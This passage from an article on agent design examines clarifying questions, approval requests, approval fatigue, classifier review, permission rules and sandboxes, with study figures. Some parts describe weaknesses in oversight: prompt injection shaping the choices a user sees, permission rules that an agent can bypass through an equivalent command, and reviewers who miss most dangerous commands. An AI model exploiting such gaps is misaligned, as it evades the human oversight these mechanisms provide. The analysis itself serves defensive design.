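Software that receives "auth-required" therefore can't determine from the state alone whether to show a login page or an approve button. The explanation is in the accompanying message, which the other agent can write in ordinary prose. Some products always treat the state as a request to log in. MuleSoft, which sells software for connecting business systems, has a component for the older version 0.3.0 that returns "auth-required" whenever a request arrives without a second access token. A client designed for that meaning could answer a request for approval by fetching a token, and the task might then continue without anyone's approval. "Input-required" is no more precise, since an approval is also user input.

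The protocol also leaves open what an approval means. According to AGNTCY, version 1.0 leaves authorisation logic to each implementation. The current working draft states that the protocol does not define the scope of a decision, how long it lasts or how to revoke it. Under the draft, entering the "auth-required" state authorises nothing by itself, and a credential that an agent obtains during one pause doesn't automatically cover later messages in the same task. Ghumare presents these two rules as part of version 1.0, while AGNTCY quotes them from the draft.

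Suppose the design firm's agent hands the invoice to another company's mail agent, which pauses for approval, and the user says yes. The protocol doesn't specify whether that approval covers one email or every email to Lindqvist, whether it still holds next week, or how the firm could withdraw it. The two companies have to agree on these points separately.

They also have to agree on how to name the action. AGNTCY points out that A2A messages have no field for the operation the sender wants, so the receiving agent infers it from the text. The harness therefore has no structured call that it can turn into an approval request like the one above. AGNTCY suggests having the sender declare the operation, but only allowing the declaration to narrow what the sender was already allowed to do. Otherwise a sender could gain permissions by claiming them. AGNTCY also sketches an authorisation record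 that would name the agents, the task, the action, the resource and an expiry time, but its software does not yet issue such records.

Requests can travel up a chain of agents to a person. If the mail agent is working for a planning agent, which is working for the user, the planning agent can pause its own task and pass the request to the user. This lets the person see both the job they originally delegated and the specific action that needs approval. Credentials should go directly to the agent that needs them because, as Ghumare notes, every agent in the chain could read them if they were passed back down the same way. MuleSoft's component looks for the token inside the message, which version 0.2.1 allowed.

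### Questions and permissions in SemaClaw

In SemaClaw, by Zhu and colleagues, a single component called the PermissionBridge handles both permission requests and questions, but gives each its own contents and replies. For a permission request, the harness saves the tool's name, the proposed arguments and a rationale, and the user can approve, deny or modify the call. The answer to a question goes back to the model like a tool result, so it informs the model's next step and does not release a waiting call.

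One PermissionBridge serves every running agent. When an agent pauses for a request, the bridge gives the request a unique ID and uses it to return the reply to the right agent. Requests can appear as buttons in the user's Telegram chat, where several agents may be waiting at once. Without the IDs, a tap meant to approve one agent's file search could approve another agent's email.

The framework's built-in tools run without approval, while user-installed tools, file operations and calls to outside services need consent every time by default. Zhu and colleagues justify this by saying the built-in tools can't affect anything outside the agent's environment. However, their list of built-in tools includes one for delivering outgoing messages, which seems to have effects outside that environment.

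*Sema Code* (2026) describes the software underneath SemaClaw. This software lets a user respond to a permission request by approving the action once, approving it permanently, rejecting it, or sending a correction in their own words. Permanent approval needs its own reply because it changes the project's security policy, which also permits future calls that the user hasn't seen. A user who wants to send one email should not end up authorising all of them.

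A correction counts as information, even though it answers a permission request. If the user replies "Send it from the accounts address instead", the software doesn't run the original call and passes the reply to the model. The model's new call should go through the permission check like any other.

### A reason, then a confirmation

The Authorization Closure Graph, the permission checker by Wang and colleagues, uses different reply formats for information and approval requests. A customer asked why they want to cancel a flight must reply with "cancellation_reason=" followed by one of the listed choices. If the cancellation can go ahead, a second message shows the exact call, the facts it relies on and any charge or refund. The customer authorises the call by replying with only the word CONFIRM. Any other text goes back into the ordinary conversation without authorising the call.

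The harness writes the confirmation from the pending call and current records, not from the model's account. In one recorded conversation, a customer wanted to cancel a reservation only if it was refundable. An agent without the checker wrongly treated the booking as still within the 24-hour refund window. The customer approved the cancellation, expecting a full refund, and the agent cancelled a booking that didn't qualify. With the checker, the agent explained that the booking wasn't eligible and offered to pass the request to a human.

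Some consequences need their own approval because they don't appear in the call. If a customer pays for a $348 flight with a $500 certificate that can't be refunded, they lose the remaining $152. The call includes the flight and the certificate but not the loss, so the harness calculates the loss and asks the customer to approve it.

The checker cut the number of unsafe tasks, those with a forbidden or unauthorised change, from 75 to 8. The reduction varied by model and type of task:

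| Tasks | Model | Unsafe tasks, policy in prompt only | Unsafe tasks with the checker | Success, policy in prompt only | Success with the checker |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Airline (50) | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 8 | 0 | 68.0% | 80.0% |
| Airline (50) | GPT-5.6-Terra | 18 | 4 | 54.0% | 66.0% |
| Airline (50) | Gemini-3.6-Flash | 23 | 2 | 72.0% | 72.0% |
| Retail (114) | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 3 | 1 | 87.7% | 85.1% |
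| Retail (114) | GPT-5.6-Terra | 15 | 1 | 67.5% | 69.3% |
| Retail (114) | Gemini-3.6-Flash | 8 | 0 | 80.7% | 82.5% |

Success fell in only one of the six rows, and only slightly, so the checker did not make agents safer just by stopping them from acting. Small differences in the success columns may be due to chance, because each model attempted each task once.

No version of the system merged questions with confirmations, so it's unclear how much of the improvement came from separating them. The nearest comparison concerns structured requests for missing facts. On the airline tasks, a version that checked calls but gave only generic feedback when something was missing had 19 unsafe tasks across the three models. A version that looked up the missing fact or asked the customer a specific question had 14, and it completed more tasks with every model. The full system, which also keeps track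 of permissions given earlier in a task, had 6. When Wang and colleagues removed only the separate approval of consequences such as the $152 loss, the number rose to 18.

They also built 936 artificial cases in which facts or permissions changed before an action ran, and allowed the user to answer up to four requests in each. A version that reused old approvals without checking for changes acted unsafely in 702 of them. A version that discarded all earlier approvals never acted unsafely, but it reached the right outcome in only 25% of cases because it used up its requests on things the user had already settled. The full system also never acted unsafely, and it reached the right outcome in 91.7% of cases. Separate message types can therefore make an agent unusable if the harness discards the user's answers. The harness should store each answer and ask again only when something relevant has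 changed.

The simulated customers in the main tests could type "CONFIRM" exactly every time. Real people would type "yes" or "ok do it" and not understand why nothing happened, so a product for the public should use a button.

### One function for everything

Agent frameworks differ in how much of this separation they provide. OpenAI's toolkit pauses a specific tool call until it is approved or rejected. AG2 has a more general function, "requires_input", which pauses a task and sends a prompt to the user's side. In the sample code on the *Advanced* page of AG2's documentation, the function that collects the reply returns whatever the person typed, as plain text.

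A plain-text reply is fine for a question like "Which Dana should get the invoice?" But if a developer uses the same function to ask "Send the invoice outside the firm?", the software has to turn the reply into a decision. If the user types "no problem, go ahead", code that searches for "no" will block the email. If they type "yes, but take out the second page", code that searches for "yes" will send it with the second page included. The developer could have the model interpret the reply instead, but then the model decides whether it has permission, and a prompt injection could influence that decision.

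A single function also causes problems when the user doesn't answer. If the user closes the window, the function might return empty text. An agent that asked whether to use a formal or a friendly greeting can reasonably pick one and continue, but an agent that asked for permission must not continue without it. A single function can't distinguish between these two cases.

A general function also obscures who is entitled to answer. To interrupt users less, a developer might let another program answer the agent's questions from the company directory. This is sensible when the agent needs an email address. But if approval requests go through the same function, the program will answer those too, and the agent will receive approval from software that nobody authorized to approve invoices.

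A developer whose framework offers only a general pause can build two functions on top of it. One takes a question and a list of choices and returns a value, and the model can call it as a tool. The other takes a pending call, shows it with two fixed buttons, and returns only "approve" or "deny", treating every other result as "deny". The model should not have access to the second function. The harness calls that function when a rule requires approval, and no other code can release a pending call.

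## Writing a request for information

Once an agent has a function for asking questions, its designer has to decide when the model should call it and what the user should see. Every question takes the user's time, and some are more trouble than the mistakes they prevent.

### When a question is worth asking

Suppose the agent is 70% confident that "Dana" means Lindqvist, the client. If it guesses wrong, the user loses 20 minutes apologising and resending the invoice. Answering a question would take the user 2 minutes, including the time to return to their own work.

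Guessing carries a 30% chance of losing 20 minutes, so its expected loss is 0.3 × 20 = 6 minutes. Asking costs 2 minutes, so the agent should ask. In general, a question is worth asking when

(1 − confidence) × loss if wrong > cost of asking.

If only one of these figures changes, the agent should act without asking when its confidence is above 90%, when a mistake would waste less than 6 minutes 40 seconds, or when asking would take more than 6 minutes.

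| Situation | Expected loss from guessing | Cost of asking | Better choice |
|---|---|---|---|
| As above | 6 minutes | 2 minutes | Ask |
| The agent is 95% confident | 1 minute | 2 minutes | Guess |
| A mistake costs only 5 minutes | 1.5 minutes | 2 minutes | Guess |
| The user is in a meeting, so a question costs 10 minutes | 6 minutes | 10 minutes | Guess |
| The agent is 99% confident, but a mistake costs 1,000 minutes | 10 minutes | 2 minutes | Ask |

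As the last row shows, a fixed rule such as "ask whenever confidence is below 80%" works badly because it ignores how serious a mistake would be. *Value of Information* (Dong, Hu and colleagues, 2026) compared such thresholds with an agent that weighs the expected gain from each question against the penalty for asking it. One test involved identifying animals, worth 1 point each, and diseases, worth 10. With a small penalty per question, the agent that weighed each question scored 14.14, and the best threshold scored 11.49. Across all tasks and penalties, that agent matched or beat the best hand-tuned alternative in 18 of 20 conditions.

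The calculation depends on the confidence figure, which usually comes from the model. If that figure is 70% but such guesses are right only half the time, the expected loss is 10 minutes rather than 6. Designers can check the figure by logging how often users choose the answer the model rated most likely. The calculation applies only to questions of fact, because predicting that a user would approve an action does not give the agent permission to take it.

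The loss from a wrong guess also depends on how easily the user can correct it. If the agent only prepares a draft, replacing the wrong Dana might take half a minute. The expected loss is 0.3 × 0.5 minutes, or 9 seconds, so the agent should write the draft without asking. *Rational Clarification by Assistive Agents via Value-of-Information Reasoning* (Nguyen-Hien, Teh and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that weighs the expected loss from guessing against the burden of asking. When simulated users could easily correct an answer, the agent often calculated that asking first would gain nothing. In a separate test of planning household tasks, it satisfied 56% to 59% of users' preferences, while a model fine-tuned to ask questions satisfied 44% and asked roughly five times as many questions.

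### Choosing which question to ask

An agent that is unsure of several things can compare the questions it might ask by their expected value of perfect information (EVPI). This measure from decision theory is how much better a decision would turn out, on average, if the agent knew the answer first. *Learning to Ask Good Questions* (Rao and Daumé, 2018) uses EVPI to rank clarifying questions about written posts, and *Structured Uncertainty guided Clarification for LLM Agents* (Suri, Mathur and colleagues, 2025) applies it to tool calls.

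Their agent lists the calls the user might want and gives each a probability. It then scores each possible question:

```
EVPI(q) = E_r[ max_c π(c | q, r) ] − max_c π(c)
```

Here q is the question, r is a possible answer, c is a candidate call, and π(c) is the probability that c is the call the user wants. The last term is the agent's chance of being right if it acts now. The term before it is the agent's chance of being right after hearing the answer, averaged over the possible answers and weighted by their probability.

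Suppose there are two Danas and also two versions of the March invoice, a final one and a draft. The agent is 70% confident in Lindqvist and 95% confident in the final version. If the two are independent, the candidates are:

| Candidate call | Probability |
|---|---|
| Final version to Lindqvist | 0.665 |
| Final version to Ortiz | 0.285 |
| Draft to Lindqvist | 0.035 |
| Draft to Ortiz | 0.015 |

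If the agent acts now, it has a 66.5% chance of being right. Asking "Which Dana?" would raise that to 95% whatever the answer, so the question has an EVPI of 0.95 − 0.665 = 0.285. Asking "Which version?" would raise it to only 70%, for an EVPI of 0.035.

These values are gains in probability, so the designer has to multiply them by the loss from a mistake before comparing them with the burden of asking. If any mistake loses 20 minutes, asking about Dana saves 5.7 minutes on average and asking about the version saves 0.7. Once the user has chosen a Dana, asking about the version saves 0.05 × 20 = 1 minute on average. That is less than the 2 minutes the question would take, so the agent should go ahead with the final version.

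A question has no value if every answer leads to the same action. For example, an agent sending Lindqvist an invoice doesn't need to ask whether Lindqvist is a long-standing client, because the invoice goes to the same address either way. *CONTRA* (2026) applies this test to programming by generating a program for each possible answer and keeping the question only if the programs behave differently. A question is also useless if the user doesn't know the answer. Someone who reports a bug can usually describe what went wrong but not which function caused it. *Asking What Matters* (2026) treats answerability as a separate requirement from relevance.

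Suri and colleagues also subtract a penalty for each earlier question about the same argument of the call. The agent stops asking when the best remaining score falls below a tenth of the leading candidate's probability. The penalty cut the number of questions by 18% to 27% and changed the quality of the results by less than 3%. But the first question about an argument carries no penalty, so a designer who wants to account for the burden of interrupting has to add a term for it.

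The method also uses the tools' data to narrow the possible answers. In one of the paper's examples, a user says "call Alex from work", and the contacts list has two people named Alex. Only one has a work number, so the agent doesn't need to ask which Alex the user means.

On ambiguous requests to GPT-4o, the agent got 59.7% of tool calls fully right and asked 1.39 questions per task. The best alternative, which put the tools' specifications in the prompt, got 55.7% right and asked 2.56 questions. The gain over that alternative is 4 percentage points; the 7% to 39% gain that Suri and colleagues report is relative. The drop in questions is more impressive, though the agent still asked 1.08 questions per task when the request left nothing out.

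The scoring also has two weaknesses. It treats every possible value of a missing argument as equally likely, so it would give each of the two Danas a 50% probability, even though invoices usually go to clients. It also counts only the candidates the model proposed, so if the user means a third Dana the model didn't list, the agent gives her a probability of zero.

### How much the answers help

Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *SWE-Clar*, measured how much coding agents gain from asking. They built 100 tasks from real software jobs on the freelance site Upwork, each of which had paid at least $4,000. The opening request left out important requirements, and the agent could question a simulated client before it started programming. Two models did all the tasks under three conditions, and a task counted only if the software passed every test:

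| Model | No questions | Questions to the client | Full requirements from the start |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 6% | 49% | 75% |
| GLM-5.3 Flash | 5% | 39% | 71% |

Asking closed 62% of the gap for the first model and 52% for the second. The rest remained, partly because agents didn't ask about some requirements and partly because they misunderstood some answers. Across the nine models in the wider study, agents misstated 3% to 6% of the hidden requirements that the client had fully explained.

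These gains are large, but the conditions favoured asking. The agents had instructions to clarify, and a real client would probably help less than this one, who knew every requirement and never got tired of answering. A second model also checked each reply for accuracy before the agent saw it.

*Ambig-SWE* (Vijayvargiya, Zhou and colleagues, 2025) found that older models rarely asked for information unless the prompt told them to, although asking improved their results by up to 74% in relative terms.

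The gain from clarification also depends on what is missing. *AM-Bench* (2026) estimates that clarification would raise the share of tasks that agents complete by 15.4 percentage points when the goal is unclear, by 8.0 when background is missing and by only 1.2 when a constraint is missing. Clarifying constraints would raise compliance more, by an estimated 4.5 points. An agent can complete a task without knowing a constraint, so a designer who measures only completion would undervalue questions about constraints.

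### How Claude Code got its question tool

In Anthropic's *Seeing like an agent* (2026), the engineer Thariq Shihipar writes that Claude could ask questions in ordinary text, but answering them felt slow. Claude Code's AskUserQuestion tool was Anthropic's third attempt to fix this.

The team first added a list of questions to the existing tool that the model calls to present a finished plan. This was the easiest change to make, but the model had to write a plan and questions about that plan at the same time. If the user's answers contradicted the plan, it was unclear whether the model should call the tool again.

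Next, the team told the model to write its questions in a text format that the harness could turn into buttons, such as bullet points with the alternatives in brackets. The model usually did this, but sometimes it added sentences, left out options or dropped the format. Software that expects a fixed format can't reliably display such questions.

Finally, the team made a separate tool for asking questions. The model can call it at any point, though its prompt particularly encourages this during planning. The harness shows the questions in a dialog box and blocks the agent's loop until the user answers, so the agent can't build on a guess in the meantime. Because a tool call has named fields, the harness doesn't have to find the questions in prose.

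Shihipar reports that the model called the tool readily and that its output worked well, but he gives no measurements. His account therefore can't show how often the text format failed, whether people answered faster with the tool, or whether the agent's work improved. It is still useful because it describes two designs that failed for reasons other developers are likely to run into.

### Options, free text, defaults and a way out

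*Spring AI Agentic Patterns (Part 2)* (Tzolov, 2026) describes a version of AskUserQuestion for Java programs. One call can hold several questions, each with a short header and two to four options. Each option has a description of what choosing it would mean. The user can pick one option, or several if the question allows it, and can always type something else.

The invoice question could look like this:

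> Which Dana should get the March invoice?
>
> - Dana Lindqvist, client, dana@lindqvist.example
> - Dana Ortiz, our accounts department, dana.ortiz@firm.example
> - Someone else (type a name)
> - I'm not sure
> - Don't send it

Questions with fixed options are quick to answer, and software can check the replies. Their value is also easier to calculate, which is why Dong and colleagues allow only multiple-choice and yes-or-no questions. Fixed options work best when the possible answers come from a known list, such as the address book. Free text is better when the agent can't predict the answers, as with "What should the covering note say?"

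"I'm not sure" and "Don't send it" need separate options because they lead to different next steps. If the user isn't sure, the agent could check who received last month's invoice. If the user no longer wants to send anything, the agent should stop. Without these options, a user who wants neither Dana has to choose one or close the window, and the harness can't determine why the window was closed.

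A default saves time when a wrong guess would do little harm. For example, "I'll use the firm's usual greeting unless you choose another" lets the agent continue if the user doesn't reply. A default is reasonable only where guessing would have been acceptable. If the agent has worked out that guessing the recipient is too risky, it shouldn't guess after ten minutes without a reply. For the same reason, the form shouldn't open with Lindqvist already selected, since a user in a hurry could submit the model's guess without reading it.

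### Asking early or late, and grouping questions

*Ask Early, Ask Late, Ask Right* (Gulati, Gupta and colleagues, 2026) tested how much the timing of an answer matters. The researchers removed information from 84 task descriptions and supplied it at set points during the agent's run. The table shows the share of tasks in which at least one of three attempts succeeded, for two of the three benchmarks: MCP-Atlas (short tasks with many tools) and SWE-Bench Pro (code repairs).

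| Benchmark and missing information | Answer after 10% of the run | After 50% | After 90% | No answer |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| MCP-Atlas, goal | 0.78 | 0.44 | 0.39 | 0.40 |
| MCP-Atlas, input data | 0.46 | 0.36 | 0.25 | 0.33 |
| SWE-Bench Pro, goal | 0.86 | 0.67 | 0.71 | 0.46 |
| SWE-Bench Pro, input data | 1.00 | 0.79 | 0.75 | 0.63 |

On MCP-Atlas, an answer about the goal lost most of its value by the middle of the run, and a very late answer about input data left agents worse off than no answer. On SWE-Bench Pro, an answer helped even when it came 90% of the way through the run. On the third benchmark, agents failed most tasks even with full information, and the timing of an answer about the goal made no clear difference. Each row covers only 18 to 28 combinations of task and model, so small differences mean little.

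Early answers are therefore better, but an agent can't ask about a gap it hasn't found. In a test on database tasks, Elfeki and colleagues found that Claude Opus 4.6 asked about 61% of the gaps when it could explore the database and 11% when it had only the task description. An agent that has to ask all its questions before it starts would miss most of the gaps.

A sensible compromise is for the agent to ask about an unclear goal immediately, then read whatever its tools can supply, and ask about the remaining gaps before taking any step that depends on them. Gulati and colleagues give the example of an agent that spends 30 actions on a quarterly report before it finds out that the user meant fiscal quarters, not calendar quarters, which it could have asked about at the start.

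Grouping questions reduces interruptions. Suppose a question takes 2 minutes of the user's time, 1.5 to switch attention and 0.5 to read and answer. The question about the invoice version was worth 1 minute, too little to justify a separate interruption. But if the agent is already asking about Dana, the version question adds only half a minute, so it is worth including. Grouping works poorly when one question depends on the answer to another. For example, the agent shouldn't ask which of Lindqvist's two addresses to use until it knows that the user means Lindqvist.

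### When the model writes the options

The way a list presents its options also influences the answer. If the model labels Lindqvist "recommended", puts her first and describes her as "the client who usually gets invoices", but lists Ortiz by name only, the user is likely to choose Lindqvist. The user may also think the label comes from the firm's records when it is the model's guess.

The list can also leave out the right answer. Tzolov's example is a travel assistant that asks about the user's interests and offers history, nature, food and cities. Someone visiting family has to notice that none of these fits and type their own answer. In the invoice example, a user who meant a third Dana might pick the closest match, assuming the agent had checked everyone.

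Prompt injection makes both problems worse. If the agent has read the stranger's message about a new billing address, it might offer "Dana Lindqvist (new billing address)" as one of the choices. The user would then choose from a list that an attacker helped write, and the real address might not be on it.

Several measures limit the risk:

- When the choices come from records, the harness should fill them in. The model can request a choice between the address book entries that match "Dana", and the harness can then list every match with its name, department and address.
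- When the model has to write the options, as with the tone of a letter, each should have the same kind of description. Zheng, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *Is That Clear?*, gave both options in each of their questions a benefit and a downside.
- The harness should add "someone else" or "something else" itself, so that the model can't omit it.
- If an option comes from outside material, the screen should show the source, for example "from an email received today from an unknown sender".
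- Designers should log how often people type their own answer. A high rate suggests that the options are missing what people want. A low rate is harder to interpret, because people may be settling for what they are offered.

### People check less after answering

Balanced options don't remove every side effect. Zheng and colleagues asked 180 people to review an assistant's recommendations for everyday decisions, such as choosing a smart lock or planning a trip. Half first answered two questions about their preferences. Each person saw three recommendations, two of which broke a requirement listed on the screen.

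People who had answered questions accepted 52% of the faulty recommendations unchanged, compared with 39% among the others. They also accepted more of the correct ones (76% against 61%) and spent an average of 55 seconds reviewing, compared with 81. They felt that the assistant understood them better, but their general trust in it did not differ significantly.

People who had answered questions accepted a faulty recommendation more often when the error was in a part that a question had covered (60%) than when it was elsewhere (43%). In one case, the assistant asked whether the person wanted to install the lock themselves. The recommendation followed that preference, but the lock would take two weeks to arrive and the deadline was one week. People may have felt that the assistant had already dealt with installation, or they may have stopped checking once they saw that the recommendation followed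 their choice. The experiment can't separate these explanations.

The participants had nothing of their own at stake when they judged the advice, so the effect may be smaller when a mistake would hurt them. Still, in the invoice example, a user who has just picked Lindqvist could make a similar mistake, seeing her name on the next screen and not noticing that the address is wrong. Zheng and colleagues suggest that software should make extra checks on whatever a question covered. Here, the harness can compare the address in the email call with the address book entry the user chose, and stop the call if they differ.

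## Choosing which actions must wait for approval

The invoice can go to the wrong address without anyone checking it if the harness holds too few tool calls for approval. The same can happen if it holds too many, because the user starts approving them without reading.

Wang and colleagues, whose survey of agent security covered 59 papers, 21 products and 26 plugins up to April 2026, found that 15 of the products ask for approval while the agent is running. They compare these designs along six dimensions:

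| Dimension | What the designer decides | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Object | What the user approves | One command, a batch of actions, a whole plan |
| Granularity | How much one decision covers | One call, one tool, the rest of the session |
| Trigger | What makes the agent pause | Any action, a dangerous pattern, the edge of a sandbox |
| Options | How the user can answer | Allow or deny, always allow, edit the call first |
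| Fatigue mitigation | How the system reduces the number of requests | Remembered approvals, approval of a plan instead of its steps |
| Information shown | What the user sees before deciding | The bare command, an explanation of the risk |

These choices affect each other. An "always allow" button is an answer option, but clicking it also changes the trigger, because the harness then holds fewer calls for approval. Permissions can therefore grow during a session, which Wang and colleagues call scope creep, and few products help users reduce them again.

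The trigger for approval requests determines how many the user gets. An agent can ask before every action, before actions in fixed categories, when a rule written by the user applies, when an action crosses a boundary, or when software estimates that an action is risky.

### Asking about every action

Asking for approval before every action needs no judgement from the designer, and a person can stop any action before it runs. But to send one invoice, the agent has to ask before it searches the address book, finds the file, opens it and sends the email, and only the last of these four requests matters. The problem is worse with coding agents, and Wang and colleagues note that asking Claude Code to reorganise a program's login code can set off dozens of requests. An agent that has to ask every time also can't work while the user is away.

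This approach fails because people pay less attention when they have to approve many mostly harmless actions, a problem called approval fatigue. The problem is older than AI agents. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, summarise earlier research in which people paid little attention to the permissions Android apps requested and often misunderstood them. Other studies found that people paid less attention to security warnings the more often they saw them.

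Designers have reduced the problem of ignored prompts before. In the 2000s, most people ignored browser warnings about insecure connections, and some experts wanted to abolish them. According to Wang and colleagues, researchers instead simplified the wording, showed the warnings less often and made the safe choice the default, and people then heeded the warnings much more.

An agent's request is harder to judge than a phone app's request to use the camera, because the user has to work out both what the action does and whether it belongs to the task. Salerno and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 about how they do this. How closely people checked a request depended on their trust in the agent, the importance of the task, the possible consequences and how much time they had. The researchers warn against treating repeated approvals as a lasting preference. A user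 who approves ten emails in a row may be happy with all of them or may have stopped reading. If the agent then offers to stop asking, it can create a permanent rule from approvals the user gave only because they were tired.

Some people switch off approval requests. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and users' files and found that weaknesses in user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, actions were approved automatically. Some users had chosen a mode that allows everything because they would otherwise have faced hundreds of requests per session.

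### How often people catch a dangerous command

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) has the largest set of figures on approval fatigue in agents. Auto mode replaces most approval requests with a classifier, a second model that checks each action and blocks those it classifies as dangerous.

Anthropic found that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests. They may still be reading the requests, because a perfect reviewer would also approve 97% if 97% of the commands were harmless. Anthropic contrasts this rate with the plans that Claude presents before starting work, 39% of which users reject. Users do push back on some requests, then, but they can reject a safe plan because they want the work done differently, so the two rates measure different kinds of judgement.

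Users' settings are stronger evidence. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without asking. Anthropic reports that 5% allow any command and another 43% allow anything run through an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as broad. A quarter of interactive sessions start with permission requests bypassed. Without automated review, these users' commands would realistically go unreviewed.

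To test whether people catch dangerous commands, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor. They worked on coding tasks in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the text of one permission request changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only the text changed, so approving it did no harm.

The testers refused the command in 143 cases (13.6%). Auto mode blocked the same commands in 937 cases (89%). The unsafe approval rate, the share of actions that a reviewer should refuse but approves, was therefore 86.4% for the testers and 11% for the classifier. Anthropic also reports how often the two disagreed, which is enough to work out the full breakdown:

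| | Classifier blocked it | Classifier allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

If every command had needed approval from both the classifier and the tester, the testers would have stopped only 6 more commands, raising the share caught from 89.0% to 89.6%.

The testers also refused fewer of the dangerous commands as requests accumulated, from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests, while the classifier's rate stayed flat. This fits approval fatigue, but fatigue within the session can't explain most of the failures, since testers approved about 83% of the dangerous commands even near the start. They may not have understood the commands, may already have had a habit of clicking "approve", or may not have cared what happened in a test environment. Cutting the number of requests would not fix all of these problems.

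Anthropic also studied real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review, using only accounts that had agreed to share their data. A model graded how much harm each session involved and how explicitly the user had asked for the harmful action. Serious harm meant damage on the scale of deleting rows from a live company database. Of the flagged sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained a seriously harmful action that the user had not explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode.

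### How much these figures show

Anthropic was testing its own product, and it benefits when customers let agents run for longer. The testers also weren't working on their own projects. People whose own files were at risk would probably read more carefully, although the experiment can't show how much more.

This objection applies less to the data from real sessions, because those users had something to lose. But they chose their own mode, so the two groups may have differed in skill or in the work they were doing. The rates cover only flagged sessions, so 6.3% is not the chance that an ordinary session with manual approval ends in serious harm.

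Human reviewers did much better in an independent experiment. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) asked 113 people without a software background to supervise an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. Some participants approved or refused every action themselves, some had a model review the actions, and the rest wrote rules in advance.

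Based on Yan's figures, people who wrote rules blocked about 40% of the seven actions, automated review blocked about 54%, and people who judged each action blocked about 60%. The gap between the last two is small enough to be due to chance, but human approval did not collapse as it did in Anthropic's test.

The most likely reasons are that participants made only 18 decisions, that the actions were everyday ones such as sending a message or spending money, and that participants had just practised judging similar examples. The two studies also used different automated reviewers. Together, the studies suggest that people can be useful reviewers when requests are few and easy to understand. Even then, Yan's participants let through about two in five of the actions they should have stopped.

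### Fixed categories

A developer can reduce the number of requests by listing the kinds of action that always wait for approval, such as outgoing email, payments and deletions. Ordinary software can apply this list, so the developer can test it, the user can predict which actions will wait, and the agent can't get around it by arguing for an exception.

Requiring approval for a whole category of actions treats very different actions alike. If all outgoing email waits, the user has to approve a lunch invitation as well as an invoice. *Safety Sentry* describes the same problem for coding agents, where writing to a scratch file can trigger the same alarm as deleting someone's home folder.

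Categories also miss actions that achieve the same result another way, such as sharing a link to the invoice instead of emailing it. Anthropic warns of a similar gap in Claude Code, where a rule requiring approval for a shell command matches the command as written, so in some configurations the agent can run it in a form the rule doesn't match. Designers should therefore define each category by what a call does, such as "sends a file outside the firm", and apply it to every tool that can do that.

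### Rules that users write

Users know things that the developer doesn't, such as which clients are sensitive and which folders hold only scratch work. They could settle many decisions in advance by writing their own rules, but they tend to write rules that settle nothing or allow too much.

Yan's participants wrote one rule for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something and accessing private information. They could choose "allow", "ask" or "never", and they chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules. Requests fell from 18 to an average of 10.9, but total time was not reliably lower once it included writing the rules.

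These participants were also the least protected. Of the 148 excessive actions that went ahead in their group, rules automatically allowed only 15. The rules left the other 133 for people to decide on later, and people approved them. Yan compared complete designs, so the study can't show why people who had written rules approved more. They may have felt already protected by the rules.

Rules that permit actions tend to be too broad. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, found that a sizeable minority of OpenAI staff who used Codex let it run any command starting with "python". Since a Python program can do almost anything, this rule removes most of the protection. One user had given standing permission for a command that starts a second copy of Codex with its safeguards off.

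Rules that forbid actions often exist only in the model's prompt, where nothing enforces them. Many developers write security rules into CLAUDE.md, a file of standing instructions that Claude Code reads. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) used a classifier to estimate that Claude Code's built-in permission controls could cover 16.6% of these rules, and labels from human annotators suggest that the true figure is lower. The controls can match only commands, file paths and web domains, so they can't enforce a rule such as "never commit secrets", which depends on what a file contains. A user who writes such a rule may believe it is a firm limit, although the model can still disregard it.

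### A boundary

A designer can limit what the agent can reach and require approval only when it needs to go further, instead of listing every action that must wait. A sandbox is a restricted environment that sets such limits for programs. In Codex's default mode, for example, the agent can read files, edit those in a chosen folder and run local commands, but it needs approval to use the network.

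Sandboxing removes most approval requests. Anthropic reports that it cut requests in Claude Code by 84%, a figure Wang and colleagues cite. In a snapshot of 10,000 agent actions at OpenAI, Trębacz and colleagues found that 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and the other 720 would have needed approval.

A sandbox boundary takes work to set up, and it protects only what is outside it. If the sandbox includes the only copy of a client's records, the agent can delete them without asking. In July 2025, an agent from the software company Replit deleted a live database. Wang and colleagues attribute this to a sandbox that gave the agent write access to production systems during a development task. If the boundary is too tight, the agent asks for approval so often that users turn the boundary off.

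A sandbox is also less useful when the task is to affect the outside world. It can let an agent search for the invoice and draft the email without interruption, but every email leaves the sandbox, whether it goes to Ortiz or to Lindqvist. The design firm needs a boundary that fits its own risks, such as one between addresses that belong to the firm and those that don't.

### Estimating the risk

Software can also judge each action in context and ask only about the risky ones. *Safety Sentry* does this with a small language model that reviews every proposed tool call and decides whether to run it, ask the user or refuse it. The model bases its decision on the task, the agent's earlier steps and, if available, a note about the user's preferences.

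The researchers trained Safety Sentry on 7,767 steps. About half came from tasks in real office software, such as ticketing, file sharing and health records, and the rest came from public benchmarks. Two language models labelled each step, and the researchers settled disagreements and checked the whole test set. On 1,436 new steps, Safety Sentry chose the right response 91.0% of the time, compared with 72.7% for Claude Opus 4.7, the best of the models not trained for this task.

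Unnecessary questions and missed questions matter more to a designer than overall accuracy. Safety Sentry asked about 5.05% of the actions it should have run without asking, and ran 4.96% of those it should have asked about. It refused 92.7% of the actions it should have refused.

A designer can shift the balance without retraining the model. Safety Sentry gives each response a probability, and it refuses whenever refusal is the most likely. Otherwise it calculates

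q = P(execute) / (P(execute) + P(ask))

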